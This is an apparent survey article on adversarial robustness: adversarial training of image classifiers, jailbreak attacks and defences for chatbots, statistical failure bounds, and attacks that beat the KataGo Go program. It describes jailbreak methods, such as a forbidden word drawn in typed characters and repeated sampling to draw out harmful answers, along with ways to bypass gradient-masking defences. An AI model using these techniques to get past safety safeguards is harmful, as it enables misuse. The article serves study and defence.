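# Behavioural robustness methods: adversarial training, filtering and formal verification of AI systems without mechanistic understanding

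## What robustness means and what counts as a guarantee

An AI system is robust if it keeps behaving acceptably on unusual inputs and on inputs chosen by an attacker. All software has to handle bad inputs, but systems that learn from data also fail in ways that other software doesn't. A few stickers can make a car's camera system misread a stop sign as a speed limit sign, and a chatbot that refuses a dangerous request may comply when the request is reworded. Adversarial machine learning is the study of such attacks and the defences against them. In *Adversarial Machine Learning*, a taxonomy for the US National Institute of Standards and Technology, Vassilev, Oprea and colleagues (2025) counted more than 11,000 papers on the subject from 2021 to July 2024.

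Engineers mostly pursue robustness without knowing how a system arrives at its behaviour. They search for inputs that make it fail and train it on them (adversarial training), put filters before and after it, or prove that certain changes to the input cannot change the output. These methods are behavioural because they work from what the system does, or from computation over its internal numbers, without needing an account of what those numbers are for. Mechanistic understanding is a checked account of which internal computations produce a given behaviour. People disagree about how much robustness behavioural methods can achieve without it.

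### Networks, classifiers and language models

Nearly all the systems discussed here are neural networks. A neural network takes in numbers, such as the pixels of an image, multiplies and adds them through many layers, and outputs other numbers. The multipliers are called weights, and they stay the same from one input to the next. The intermediate results for a particular input are called activations. Training adjusts the weights in small steps to reduce a measure of error. Each step uses the gradient, which lists how much the error would change if each weight moved slightly. An attacker can compute the gradient for the input instead of the weights and find which pixels to change to increase the error.

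A classifier sorts inputs into classes, such as stop sign and speed limit, or harmful and harmless. An image classifier normally gives one label per image, so we can ask whether it fails on that image. A language model works on tokens, which are words or pieces of words. *Sound Probabilistic Safety Bounds for Large Language Models* (Nazeri, Schmuck et al., 2026) defines a language model as a function that takes a sequence of tokens and returns a probability for every token that could come next. To write an answer, a chatbot draws one token according to those probabilities, adds it to the sequence and repeats. Because the draws are random, a chatbot can refuse a prompt a thousand times and then give a harmful answer to the same prompt, so we have to ask how often it fails on that prompt.

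### The attacker has to be specified

A claim of robustness means little without an explicit threat model, which states what the attacker wants, knows and is allowed to change. Carlini, Athalye and colleagues (2019) argue in *On Evaluating Adversarial Robustness* that without one, a claim is usually either impossible to refute or trivially false. For example, an attacker who is allowed to rewrite the model's weights or replace the image with a different one will always succeed.

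In the usual threat model, someone attacking a classifier that reads road signs knows everything about it, including its weights. The attacker may change every pixel of a photograph by at most a small amount ε, and wants the classifier to give any wrong label. All the pictures within that limit make up the perturbation set. Carlini and colleagues concede that this model is a poor match for real attackers, who have no reason to respect ε. They defend it because it is precise enough to work on, and because a classifier that fails under this model will almost certainly fail under looser rules.

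For a chatbot, the attacker may know only what any customer can see, can type anything over as many conversations as the service allows, and wants working instructions for something forbidden. A prompt that gets past the safeguards is a jailbreak. Nobody has a good equivalent of ε for chatbot prompts. Vassilev and colleagues describe an attack in which the user draws the forbidden word as a picture made of typed characters, and a chatbot that had correctly blocked the prompt with the plain word gives the harmful information. A human reader would see the two prompts as the same request, even though they are very different strings of characters.

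The strength of an attack depends heavily on what the attacker knows. White-box attacks use full knowledge of the system, black-box attacks use little or none beyond the ability to send queries, and grey-box attacks fall in between. Tests usually assume white-box access even when a real attacker would not have it. This follows Kerckhoffs' principle from cryptography, that a defence should hold even when the enemy knows how it works. *Adversarial Alignment for LLMs Requires Simpler, Reproducible, and More Measurable Objectives* (2025) gives the practical reason that if a system depends on a secret, revealing the secret puts the whole system at risk. Differences in what attackers know also mean that attack success rates, the shares of attempts or target requests on which attacks work, are not comparable across threat models. *Physical AI* (2026), a survey of robots and other embodied systems,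 makes this point about sabotage planted in training and stickers applied afterwards.

### Four strengths of assurance

The weakest evidence of robustness is that a system passes ordinary tests, which use a fixed list of questions or known attacks. These are chosen before the defence exists, or at least without taking it into account. *Obfuscated Gradients Give a False Sense of Security* (2018) defines an adaptive attack, by contrast, as one that is built after the defence is completely specified, uses knowledge of that defence, and is restricted only by the threat model.

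The difference can be large. In *A Layered Input-Output Defense for Open-Weight Language Models under Adaptive Jailbreak Attack* (2026), researchers tried 100 forbidden requests on a language model with and without a defence that checks both what goes in and what comes out. Fixed attacks obtained 33 of the 100 without the defence and 11 with it. Adaptive attacks obtained 72 and 48. Even an attacker who never saw the model's replies got 70 and 41. The defence did help, but someone who had read only the fixed test would have expected it to stop about nine requests in ten, and against an attacker who adjusted to it, it stopped about half. The help also had a price. On one of the models, each extra percentage point of harmless requests wrongly refused bought a fall of only 2.9 points in attack success. (A system that refuses everything is impossible to jailbreak, which is why Carlini and colleagues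 want every defence to come with its performance when nobody is attacking.)

Surviving an adaptive attack is much better evidence, but its strength depends on how good the attacker is. Tramèr, Carlini and colleagues (2020), in *On Adaptive Attacks to Adversarial Example Defenses*, bypassed thirteen published defences whose designers had already tried adaptive attacks. Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025), in *The Attacker Moves Second*, bypassed twelve defences for language models. The original evaluations of most of these defences found attack success rates near zero, but the new attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of the twelve. Designers are often misled by gradient masking, in which the defence flattens or scrambles the gradient. Attacks that follow the gradient then fail, and the designers conclude that there are no bad inputs to find. Those inputs still exist, and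 an attacker can reach them by querying the model or using the gradient of a similar one.

A statistical bound is a claim of another sort, about how often failures happen. Suppose that a system fails on a fraction p of inputs and a tester draws n inputs independently. The chance that all n pass is (1 − p)ⁿ. The tester who sees a clean run asks how large p could be before a run that lucky had a probability of only 5%:

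(1 − p)ⁿ = 0.05, so n × ln(1 − p) = ln 0.05 ≈ −3.

For small p, ln(1 − p) is approximately −p, so p ≈ 3/n, which is known as the rule of three. In *Probability of adverse events that have not yet occurred*, Eypasch, Lefering and colleagues (1995) urged surgeons who were reporting no complications from keyhole operations to use this rule. If 300 patients in a row come through unharmed, the risk could still be as high as 1 in 100.

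If a million independent tests produce no failures, the failure rate is at most about 3 in a million, with 95% confidence. That would be excellent for most products, but at a billion queries a day it still allows 3,000 failures a day. ChatGPT received over 2.5 billion messages a day in mid-2025, according to UNU's *What over 2.5 Billion Daily Messages Reveal About ChatGPT Use*, and at 2.5 billion the same bound allows 7,500. The true number may be zero, but a million tests cannot establish that. Lowering the bound to one failure a day at a billion queries would take three billion tests without a failure. Carlini and colleagues calculate that a million random tests have just under a 0.1% chance of catching a fault that occurs one time in a billion.

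Small tests are even weaker because a language model's answers vary randomly. *Estimating Tail Risks in Language Model Output Distributions* (Angell, Singhal and colleagues, 2026) tested several models on 313 harmful requests without jailbreaks. When Llama-3.1-8B, a small open model, chose the most probable token at each step, it responded harmfully to 1.6% of the requests. With 10,000 randomly sampled answers per request, 74% of the requests produced at least one harmful answer. An attacker could therefore get harmful answers from this model to most of these requests just by repeating them enough times.

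These figures hold only for the distribution from which the tester drew. Angell and colleagues found that harmless rewordings of a request could shift the probability of a harmful answer by several orders of magnitude. *Forecasting Rare Language Model Behaviors* (Jones, Tong and colleagues, 2025) distinguishes two problems. Queries in deployment may differ in kind from those in the test, and even if they do not, there will be vastly more of them. To partly address the second problem, Jones, Tong and colleagues estimate how likely each test query is to produce the bad behaviour, then extrapolate from the few most likely to do so. When they extrapolated from 900 queries to 90,000, 86% of their forecasts of misuse came within a factor of ten of the true risk. But they assume that the queries keep coming from the same source and that adversaries do not adapt. An attacker does not sample from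 the tester's distribution. If one prompt in a trillion works, random testing will practically never find it, but an attacker who does can use it every time. A statistical bound on risk in ordinary use is therefore not simply better than a good adaptive test, which covers malicious use.

A proof over a perturbation set gives a deterministic guarantee. It establishes that no change of up to ε per pixel alters the label of a given photograph, so it covers an enormous number of images that nobody has ever made. The program that produces the proof must be sound, meaning that it proves only true claims. Carlini and colleagues point out that even a sound proof applies only to particular photographs and implies nothing about new ones. Vassilev and colleagues add that verification requires a lot of computation, scales badly and supports only some of the arithmetic operations that networks use.

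Before proving anything about a language model, researchers must define the property they want to prove. This is difficult because "the answer is harmless", unlike "the label stays the same", is not a mathematical statement. Nazeri and colleagues leave the judgement to an oracle, which may be a list of banned words, another classifier or a human moderator, so any guarantee is subject to the oracle's mistakes. Another approach is to prove something about the software around the model. *Composable Trust for Language Models* (2026) proves a limit on what a model's output can authorise, and adaptive attackers failed in all 12 attempts to get an action authorised. The researchers had no such proof for the defence inside the model's own processing, which they could only measure and improve.

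### Bounds from above and from below

Attacks give an upper bound on a classifier's robustness, and proofs give a lower bound. Suppose a classifier labels 100 photographs correctly, and the question is how many would keep their label under every permitted change. If an attack finds changes that fool the classifier on 40 of them, the answer is at most 60, and a better attack could only lower that bound. If a verifier proves 35 of the photographs safe, the answer is at least 35, and a better verifier could only raise that bound. The 60 is the classifier's empirical robustness, meaning its success against the attacks that someone tried, and the 35 is its certified robustness. Nobody has fooled the classifier on the remaining 25 photographs or proved them safe, so reporting 60 as the answer assumes that no better attack exists.

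A lower bound on harm is an upper bound on robustness, which causes some confusion. Nazeri and colleagues compute a guaranteed lower bound on the probability that a model answers one fixed prompt harmfully. The model assigns an exact probability to every possible answer, so the sum of the probabilities of the harmful answers they find cannot exceed the true figure. The bound is rigorous, but it proves that the model is at least that harmful on the prompt, so, like a successful attack, it gives users evidence of failure rather than assurance of safety.

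### Knowing when a system fails and knowing why

A failure mode is a kind of input or situation in which a system fails in a recognisable way. People can describe it from behaviour alone, for example by noting that a chatbot answers a request it would otherwise refuse when the forbidden word is presented as a drawing. That is enough to collect more such drawings, train on them or build a filter for them. People can also explain the failure mechanistically, by finding the computations that detect the forbidden word and showing why the drawing does not trigger them even though the model can still read it. Such an explanation, if correct, might predict other disguises before anyone has tried them.

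A method can rely heavily on a model's internals and still count as behavioural if it does not explain them. For example, to find rare harmful answers faster, both Angell and colleagues and Nazeri and colleagues average a model's activations over harmful examples, subtract the average over harmless ones, and push the model in the direction of the difference. Explaining why something happened also does not always require a full mechanistic understanding. Someone who diagnoses gradient masking understands why an attack failed, which is very useful, but may have no idea how the network recognises a stop sign.

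The case for behavioural methods is largely that they already exist and that anyone can measure their effects. A developer can apply them this week to a model that nobody understands, compare the result with last month's, and check whether the model has become less accurate or refuses more requests needlessly. Vassilev and colleagues acknowledge the lack of guarantees but still think adversarial testing is worthwhile, because it can close off many routes and make an attack take more effort than most attackers will make. Behavioural knowledge can also become more systematic. *Rare Event Analysis of Large Language Models* (2026) uses methods from statistical physics to estimate how often rare outputs occur and then study what they have in common, on the ground that predicting and controlling them depends on knowing their properties.

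Sceptics reply that tests cannot cover inputs nobody thought of. The record of broken defences supports them, as does a theoretical result that Vassilev and colleagues cite: as long as a model has any probability of an unwanted behaviour, some prompt will trigger it. Training that makes the behaviour rarer without removing it therefore does not eliminate such prompts. A proof does cover inputs nobody thought of, but only within a perturbation set that someone has specified. Defenders of behavioural methods can answer that an explanation may also be wrong or incomplete, and that the way to find out is to test it. The disagreement is therefore about whether, for particular failures, an explanation available at the time would have revealed the problem sooner than a more determined attacker did, and what resources that would have taken.

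## Image classifiers trained on their own worst cases

Researchers usually test defences for image classifiers on CIFAR-10, a set of 60,000 small colour photographs in ten classes such as cat, ship and truck. They train a network on 50,000 of the photographs and test it on the other 10,000. Each photograph is 32 by 32 pixels with three colour values per pixel, so the network receives 3,072 numbers. The attacker can usually change each number by at most ε = 8/255, which is 8 steps on the 0 to 255 scale that computers use for colour. On the public leaderboard RobustBench, an ordinarily trained network correctly labels 94.78% of the test photographs without an attack and 0.0% with one.

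### Why invisible changes add up

In *Intriguing Properties of Neural Networks*, Szegedy, Zaremba and colleagues (2013) searched for the smallest change that would make a network mislabel a photograph, and found changes too small to see. Other networks often mislabelled the altered photographs too. In *Explaining and Harnessing Adversarial Examples*, Goodfellow, Shlens and Szegedy (2014) proposed that these errors happen because tiny effects add up across thousands of input values.

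Take a classifier that multiplies each of the 3,072 numbers by a weight, adds up the results, and gives the label "cat" if the total is above zero. Suppose that the weights have an average size of 0.01, ignoring their signs. The attacker raises every number with a positive weight by 8/255 and lowers every number with a negative weight by the same amount, so all the changes push the total upwards. It rises by

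3,072 × 0.01 × 8/255 ≈ 0.96.

No pixel has changed visibly, but any photograph that scored between −0.96 and 0 is now classified as a cat. Random changes of the same size would mostly cancel out, typically shifting the total by only about 0.017 if every weight has a size of 0.01. Ordinary camera noise therefore does far less harm than an attacker.

A neural network isn't linear, but over a small enough region it behaves almost as if it were, and the gradient shows which way to push each number. Goodfellow and colleagues used this in the fast gradient sign method (FGSM), which computes the gradient once and moves every number by the full ε:

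x + ε · sgn(∇ₓL(θ, x, y)).

Here x is the photograph, y its correct label, θ the network's weights and L the loss, a measure of the network's error. The function sgn keeps only the sign of each entry in the gradient. Goodfellow and colleagues also trained networks on the altered photographs, an early form of adversarial training.

### Training against a stronger attack

Mądry, Makelov and colleagues (2017), in *Towards Deep Learning Models Resistant to Adversarial Attacks*, started from the guarantee they wanted and worked back to a training method. They looked for the weights that solve

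min over θ of E[ max over δ in S of L(θ, x + δ, y) ],

where S is the perturbation set, δ is a change from that set, and E is the average over photographs and their labels. The inner maximum is the attacker's problem of finding the most damaging change to each photograph. The outer minimum is the trainer's problem of finding weights for which even that change does little damage.

Nobody can solve the inner problem exactly for a large network, so Mądry and colleagues approximated it with projected gradient descent (PGD), which takes several small steps where FGSM takes one big one:

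1. Start from a random point within ε of the original photograph.
2. Compute the gradient of the loss for each of the 3,072 numbers and keep only its sign.
3. Move each number by a small amount α in the direction of the sign.
4. If a number is now more than ε from its original value, move it back to the edge of the permitted range. This is the projection.
5. Repeat from the second step.

Suppose a colour value was originally 100, with ε = 8 and α = 2, and the random start puts it at 103. If the gradient stays positive, the value goes to 105, then 107, then 109, which the projection cuts back to 108. If the gradient's sign flips, the next step lowers the value. FGSM cannot change direction because it computes the gradient only once.

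The outer step is ordinary training on the altered photographs. For CIFAR-10, Mądry and colleagues ran seven PGD steps on each photograph, kept the correct label, and adjusted the weights to reduce the loss on the altered version. They then had to run the attack again because the network had changed. Danskin's theorem shows that these weight updates lower the worst-case loss if the loss is smooth and the attack finds the true maximum. Neither condition quite holds for real networks, but the loss fell steadily in practice.

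The adversarially trained network labelled 87.3% of unaltered test photographs correctly, compared with 95.2% for the same design with ordinary training. It got 56.1% right under FGSM, 50.0% under seven steps of PGD and 45.8% under twenty. Network size also mattered. In experiments on handwritten digits, very small networks could learn the ordinary task but gave every image the same label when trained against PGD.

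If the inner maximum were exact and the loss close to zero, no permitted change could fool the network on those photographs. PGD finds a strong attack, but a stronger one may exist. To see how likely that was, Mądry and colleagues ran PGD from 100,000 random starting points around each of a few images. The final losses clustered tightly, and they conjectured that no attack relying on gradients alone would do much better. This is good evidence, but the robustness it supports is still empirical, and they acknowledged that isolated worse inputs could exist.

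### Single-step training and hidden gradients

Training on FGSM examples takes much less computation, and it works when the permitted change to an image is small. *Catastrophic Overfitting, Entropy Gap and Participation Ratio* (2025) tested it at several sizes of permitted change and found that at 2/255, an FGSM-trained network kept 74.72% accuracy under a strong set of attacks. At 12/255, accuracy was still 80.23% on unaltered photographs but fell to 0.00% under attack.

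The linear explanation accounts for both results. Within 2/255 of a photograph, the loss is nearly linear, so one step along the gradient lands near the worst point. Over larger distances the loss curves, and FGSM produces only a narrow range of altered photographs. As Mądry and colleagues observed, the network can learn to handle those, which gives it an excellent score against FGSM, but remain defenceless against PGD. One of the three modified single-step methods in the 2025 comparison also fell to 0.00% at 12/255, while the other two kept 30.17% and 32.13%.

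FGSM training hides a network's weakness by accident, but some other defences obscure the gradient deliberately. *Obfuscated Gradients Give a False Sense of Security* examined nine defences from a leading 2018 conference that were claimed, without proof, to withstand attackers with full knowledge of them. Seven depended on obscured gradients. Some first cleaned up the photograph with an operation that had no usable gradient. The attackers ran the cleaning normally but computed the gradient as if it had left the photograph unchanged, which was accurate enough because a cleaned photograph looks much like the original. Against defences that added randomness, they averaged the gradient over many random draws. Where a long loop made the gradient vanish or explode, they rewrote the problem to avoid following the gradient through the loop. Six of the seven defences failed completely and the other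 failed partly. PGD training did not depend on obscured gradients, and the network of Mądry and colleagues still scored 47% under attack.

According to the same study, designers can tell that something is wrong with a test if one-step attacks beat many-step attacks, or if attackers who cannot see the gradient beat those who can. An attack with no limit on ε should always succeed, so if it fails, the attack is flawed.

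### Progress since 2018

Researchers now usually compare defences with AutoAttack, which combines four attacks, some with access to the gradient and some without. It is considerably tougher than PGD alone. In the 2025 study of single-step training, one network scored 51.31% under 50 steps of PGD and 42.43% under AutoAttack. *Algorithms for Adversarially Robust Deep Learning* (2025) derived a different attack from a reformulation of adversarial training and got almost the same results as AutoAttack. This is some evidence that the scores do not depend on the design of one attack.

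The leaderboard's top entry is from *Adversarial Robustness Limits via Scaling-Law and Human-Alignment Studies* (Bartoldson, Diffenderfer and colleagues, 2024). The leaderboard lists nothing published after 2024, so it omits a higher score reported in *Vision Transformers Beat WideResNets on Small Scale Datasets Adversarial Robustness* (Wu, Song and colleagues, 2025). That paper used a vision transformer, a network design borrowed from language models. All the defended networks below use adversarial training.

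| Year | What was new | Accuracy without attack | Accuracy under AutoAttack |
|---|---|---|---|
| 2018 | PGD training (Mądry and colleagues) | 87.14% | 44.04% |
| 2019 | Extra unlabelled photographs | 89.69% | 59.53% |
| 2023 | 50 million computer-generated photographs | 93.25% | 70.69% |
| 2024 | 300 million generated photographs and a larger network (Bartoldson and colleagues) | 93.68% | 73.71% |
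| 2025 | Vision transformer with long training (Wu and colleagues) | 95.76% | 74.97% |

A few papers report higher figures, which should be read with more caution. *DIGN* (2026) reports about 75.8% under two adaptive attacks for a defence that adds random noise. Huang, Chen and Lin (2026) explain in *Expanding the Role of Diffusion Models for Robust Classifier Training* that RobustBench excludes defences that use randomness when classifying because adaptive attacks frequently break them. Wang (2026) reports 76.4% in *Sensitivity as a Double-Edged Sword* after replacing the final layer of the 2024 network. Wang warns that the new layer obscures gradients, and so attacked it through substitute models.

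MeanSparse, an earlier attempt to improve the same network, shows why outside attacks matter. It added an operation to the network and raised its AutoAttack score from 73.71% to 75.28%. An attack adapted to the new operation then lowered the score to 73.10%, slightly below the unmodified network's score. The leaderboard records both 75.28% and 73.10%, but *VanillaBench* (Bunzel, 2026) still lists MeanSparse as the most robust model at 75.28%.

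### What the progress cost

Each step of adversarial training takes about nine times as much computation as an ordinary training step. Bartoldson and colleagues measure computation in forward passes, which are single runs of the network on an input. An ordinary step takes the equivalent of three forward passes, one to get the answer and two to work out how to change the weights. An adversarial step takes about 27, including 20 for ten PGD steps.

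Their best network used over 10²¹ arithmetic operations. To see how much more computation would help, they trained a range of networks on different amounts and qualities of generated data and fitted curves to the results. The curves level off near 90%, and reaching that level would take around 10³⁰ operations, roughly a billion times as many. They estimate that this would take about 3,000 years on 25,000 of the best chips of the time. The forecast applies only to this way of training, and better algorithms or data could change it.

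The curves stop at 90% partly because the attack alters some photographs too much for people to label them correctly. Three members of the research team looked at the 2,629 altered photographs that the network got wrong. They often got them wrong too, and the team judged 727 invalid because the original object was no longer recognisable or the picture clearly showed something else. Assuming that people would correctly label every photograph the network got right, average human accuracy was 90.46%. Without the invalid photographs, the network scored 79.49% and the humans 96.46%.

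These human figures come from three people who all worked on the study. The comparison also favours humans, because the attacker designed the changes to fool the network, not those three people. But the invalid photographs do reveal a flaw in the perturbation set, because a change of 8/255 per number was supposed to leave the object recognisable and sometimes doesn't when the attacker targets a robust network.

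Robust networks are also less accurate on unaltered images. Bunzel compared the 98 CIFAR-10 networks then on this part of RobustBench with undefended ones. On average, the robust networks were 12.01 percentage points less accurate than the best undefended model and 7.59 points less accurate than undefended networks of the same or a similar design. The ten most robust did better, averaging 93.65% against 99.5% for the best undefended model, but they still made about thirteen times as many mistakes. On CIFAR-100, a similar set with 100 classes, robust networks were on average 17.47 points less accurate than undefended networks of similar design.

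More training data reduces this loss. When Wu and colleagues trained a vision transformer on only the real CIFAR-10 photographs, its accuracy was 77.16% without an attack and 56.85% under 40 steps of PGD. With nine generated images added for every real one, these figures rose to 94.40% and 73.77%. Vision transformers need unusually large amounts of data, so other designs may gain less, but part of the apparent trade-off between accuracy and robustness clearly comes from a shortage of examples.

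### Changes that the training did not cover

All the scores above concern small changes to every colour value. A sticker on a stop sign changes a few pixels by a lot, and a rotated photograph may differ from the original at nearly every pixel. Neither attack stays within 8/255, so the training gives no assurance against them. *Obfuscated Gradients Give a False Sense of Security* noted in 2018 that training on one measure of change gives only limited robustness under others. Robustness can also fail against larger changes of the same kind. The digit classifier of Mądry and colleagues held up well at the ε used in training, but its accuracy dropped sharply at slightly larger values.

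Some protection carries over. Mądry and colleagues also attacked the digit classifier under a limit on the overall size of the change (the square root of the sum of its squares), which lets an attacker alter a few pixels heavily. The classifier did fairly well at a size of 4.5, on a scale where each pixel runs from 0 to 1. But a change of that size spread evenly over a digit's 784 pixels is only about 0.16 per pixel, well within the limit of 0.3 per pixel used in training, so only the more concentrated changes were new to the network. The attack was again PGD, and a stronger one might have done more damage.

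Developers can add more kinds of change to the training, but this takes more computation. They have to think of each kind first, and the list has no obvious end. Certified training, which aims to produce networks that can be proved robust, has the same limitation.

### Whether explaining the failures helped

The best-known attempt to explain adversarial examples is *Adversarial Examples Are Not Bugs, They Are Features* (Ilyas, Santurkar and colleagues, 2019). It proposed that photographs contain faint patterns that predict the label but that people don't notice. A network trained only for accuracy will use any pattern that helps. Many of these patterns are fragile, so an attacker can reverse them with an invisible change to the image.

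In their main experiment, they altered a photograph of a dog slightly, until an ordinary network labelled it a cat, although a person would still see a dog. They then added it to a new training set with the label "cat". They did this for the whole training set, with target classes chosen at random, and trained a new network on the result. To a human, nearly all the labels were wrong, but the new network labelled about 63% of the unaltered test photographs correctly. It could not have learned the right labels from the visible objects, so the invisible changes must have carried information about what real cats and dogs look like.

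With random targets, the visible object might still have been slightly informative about the label, for instance because some changes also strengthened visible features of the target class. To address this, a second version gave all the images in a class the same wrong target, so that all the dogs, for example, were labelled as horses. A classifier that relied on the visible object would then learn the wrong label for every class. Accuracy on normal photographs fell to about 44%, still far above chance.

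The journal *Distill* published several replies that year. Gabriel Goh found that visible features explained some of the success with random targets, but found no such effect in the second version. Preetum Nakkiran showed that some adversarial examples are just bugs by constructing changes that fooled one network but carried no useful information. A new network trained on them did not learn to classify normal photographs. Ilyas and colleagues accepted that such examples can exist, since they had claimed only that useful fragile patterns exist and account for much of the problem. Li, Wang and colleagues (2023) argued in *Adversarial Examples Are Not Real Features* that the fragile patterns are much less useful when networks learn without labels, for example by filling in missing parts of images. This suggests that the patterns are more like shortcuts for one kind of task than general facts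 about photographs.

The explanation also suggests why an attack on one network often works on another, since both have learned the same fragile patterns, and why robust networks lose accuracy, since they give up patterns that help on normal photographs. It was less useful for building defences. Ilyas and colleagues produced a training set with most of the fragile patterns removed, and ordinary training on it gave a moderately robust network, but making the set required a network that had already gone through adversarial training. Most of the later gains on RobustBench came from generated data, larger networks and more computation, none of which depended on knowing which patterns were fragile.

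Some results suggest that knowledge of a network's internals can help. Wang argues from geometry that the usual final layer is too sensitive to small shifts in the activations, and designed the replacement to be less sensitive. If the 2.3-point gain holds up against attacks by other people, a partial explanation will have led to a better defence. Huang and colleagues noticed a weak tendency for robust classifiers to have activations resembling those of a diffusion model, an image generator that learns by removing noise from pictures. They also noticed that the diffusion model's activations responded less to fine-grained noise. Adding a term to adversarial training that rewards the resemblance improved accuracy with and without attacks. They then used interpretability tools to study why, and found that the trained networks kept their internal features more separate. They had arrived at the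 method through correlations, and did the mechanistic analysis after it already worked.

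## KataGo: retraining a superhuman Go program against attack

Researchers can't always say whether an image classifier has failed, because some attacks change a photograph so much that people no longer agree on what it shows. Go doesn't have this problem, since the rules settle which moves are legal and who has won. The best Go programs are also far stronger than any person, so one might expect them to be hard to fool, or at least easy to fix once fooled.

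In Go, two players take turns placing black and white stones on a 19 by 19 grid, and whoever controls more of the board at the end wins. Adjacent stones of one colour form a group. The empty points next to a group are its liberties, and the opponent captures the group by filling the last of them.

KataGo is an open-source program that David Wu published in 2019. It learned mostly by playing against itself. Its neural network takes in a position and outputs promising moves and an estimate of who will win. Before choosing a move, KataGo also searches through possible continuations. Search is measured in visits, each of which is roughly one position examined. In *Adversarial Policies Beat Superhuman Go AIs*, Wang, Gleave and colleagues (2022) estimated that the strongest version at the time played like a weak professional without search, and that with more than 128 visits per move it played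 better than any human.

### An opponent trained to beat one program

The threat model limits the attacker to legal moves. The attacker can run KataGo's network on any position but cannot see the weights or compute gradients, and KataGo stays frozen throughout.

Wang and colleagues trained a much smaller network to attack KataGo by having it play KataGo repeatedly and learn only from its own moves. When the attacker searched ahead, it used KataGo's network to predict KataGo's replies. An attacker that loses every game learns very little, so training began against an early, weak version of KataGo without search. Each time the attacker won often enough, the researchers gave it a stronger opponent. The last was KataGo's strongest network, searching with 131,072 visits per move.

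The researchers' first attacker won 99.9% of its games against KataGo without search by getting it to pass too early, which ended the game while the attacker was ahead. They then added a hand-written rule that stopped KataGo from passing while a move could still change the result, and the attacker lost all 1,000 test games. But the rule also blocked passing in some positions where passing is correct because any move loses stones, and another attacker learned to set up those positions.

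Repeating the training against the patched program produced a much more serious attack. The new attacker won all 1,048 games when patched KataGo played without search and 95.7% when it used 4,096 visits. Against the unpatched program, it won 97.3% at 4,096 visits. In samples of 50 games, it won 82% at a million visits and 72% at ten million, which takes more than an hour per move on a high-end home computer.

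This attacker is bad at Go. A novice on the research team beat it, and after more than 2,300 games on a public server it ranked around 17 kyu, a beginner's grade. Yet it beats KataGo, which beats professionals. General playing strength can't explain that, so the attacker must be exploiting something particular to KataGo.

Other Go programs share the weakness. Without further training, the attacker won 6.1% of games against Leela Zero and 3.5% against ELF OpenGo, two programs that even the best humans almost never beat. Kellin Pelrine, a Go expert on the team, studied the attacker's games and learned to play the strategy without a computer's help. Pelrine won 14 of 15 games against the top-ranked KataGo bot on the server, and also won after giving it nine free stones at the start, an advantage that would almost certainly let a human professional beat anyone. Other people have since used the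 same idea against several leading programs.

### The ring of stones

The attack relies on KataGo building a group that loops around and joins up with itself. In one game that Wang and colleagues describe, it went as follows:

1. The attacker played poor opening moves, and before move 10 KataGo put its own chance of winning above 90%.
2. From move 20, the attacker built a small group that looked doomed. KataGo surrounded it, and the surrounding stones eventually formed a ring.
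3. From move 74, the attacker slowly surrounded the ring from outside, over more than 100 moves.
4. Until move 189, KataGo could have saved the ring with moves that a person who had played for a few months might have found. It played elsewhere, lost the ring, and with it the game.

For most of such a game, KataGo typically estimates its chance of winning at more than 99%, and this estimate often collapses only one move before the capture. Wu hypothesises that the network passes information about liberties from stone to stone along a group, and on a ring cannot detect when that information has returned to its starting point. It would then count the same liberties several times, so a ring with four liberties left might look as if it had eight or twelve and seem perfectly safe.

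More search helps to some extent. With 500,000 visits, KataGo found a winning move in eight of ten positions where it had made the losing mistake at 1,600 visits. But the attacker that the researchers trained against deeper search set longer traps. When it beat KataGo at ten million visits, the last chance to save the ring came 8.4 moves before the capture on average, compared with 6.4 in the games where KataGo searched less. In five other positions, KataGo still chose a losing move after a billion visits.

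### Three ways of retraining

Wu began adversarial training in December 2022. He picked positions from the attacker's games by hand and had KataGo start 0.08% of its self-play games from them. By May 2023 the original attacker had lost all 400 test games at 1,600 visits. Wang and colleagues then trained the attacker further against the retrained networks, and it won 47% of games at 4,096 visits, still by capturing rings of stones.

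Tseng, McLean and colleagues (2024) tested three defences in *Can Go AIs Be Adversarially Robust?* One was Wu's training on chosen positions, which by then made up a few tenths of a percent of games. A newly trained ring attacker won 65% of games against the December 2023 network at 4,096 visits. Another attacker, which did not rely on rings, got KataGo to give away two stones in a position where the rule against repeating an earlier position stopped KataGo from capturing one back. This "gift" attack won 91% of games at 512 visits, but its win rate fell sharply with more search.

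Wu added positions from both attacks to KataGo's training. Against the network of May 2024, the ring attacker's win rate dropped from 65% to 3%, and the gift attacker's from 91% to 0%. Tseng and colleagues then trained another attacker, which captured larger, oblong rings and won 75% of games at 4,096 visits.

The second defence alternated attack and retraining for nine rounds, much like the min-max training of image classifiers. In each round, KataGo played 18% of its games against the latest attacker and the rest against itself. The attacker then trained against the improved KataGo. With a moderate amount of search, each new version beat nearly all the earlier attackers. The final version was still superhuman, though slightly weaker than the starting version. But the ninth attacker, which it had never trained against, beat it in 59% of games at 4,096 visits.

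KataGo's network is convolutional, so it combines information from small neighbourhoods of the board. Wu had suggested that such a network learns a local rule for whether a group is safe, and that the rule fails on large groups. A vision transformer can relate distant points directly, so Tseng and colleagues also trained one from scratch by self-play. It won two of three games against professionals, but a new ring attacker beat it in 78% of games. Even the original attacker, trained only on KataGo, won 2.5% of games against the transformer at 512 visits.

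This table combines results from Wang and colleagues and Tseng and colleagues. The last column includes training that an attacker inherited from earlier ones.

| Program attacked | Attacker's win rate at 4,096 visits | Win rate with more search | Attacker's training computation as a share of the program's |
|---|---|---|---|
| KataGo without adversarial training, 2022 | 97% | 72% at 10 million visits | 10% |
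| Chosen positions, May 2023 | 47% | 17.5% at 100,000 visits | 13% |
| Chosen positions, December 2023 | 65% | 27% at 65,536 visits | 13% |
| Chosen positions, May 2024 | 75% | 56% at 65,536 visits | 9% |
| Nine rounds of attack and retraining | 59% | 42% at 65,536 visits | 26% |
| Vision transformer | – | 78% at 65,536 visits | 467% |

The vision transformer's 467% is high because the program had little training. Adapting the original attacker to this program took about 73% as much computation as training the program. Each row has a different attacker, so the rise in win rates from 2023 to 2024 doesn't show that KataGo was getting worse.

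The transformer result makes convolution an unlikely cause. Tseng and colleagues think self-play is the most likely remaining one. A program trained only against copies of itself faces opponents with the same blind spot, so neither side has a reason to explore rings.

Combining the two designs may work better. In *Bridging Local and Global Knowledge via Transformer in Board Games*, Ju, Wu and colleagues (2024) alternated convolutional and transformer layers. On 24 recorded games by the original attacker, the probability of a successful attack fell from 70.44% to 23.91%. But that attacker had trained against KataGo, so the result doesn't show how the combined network would do against an attacker trained on it.

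### How much harder the attacks became

None of these defences comes with a proof of robustness. In tests, the retrained programs were robust against attackers they had already faced, but new attackers beat them, mostly with variations on the ring. The programs had to learn each variation separately, whereas a person who can beat one can beat them all, because to a person they are the same trick.

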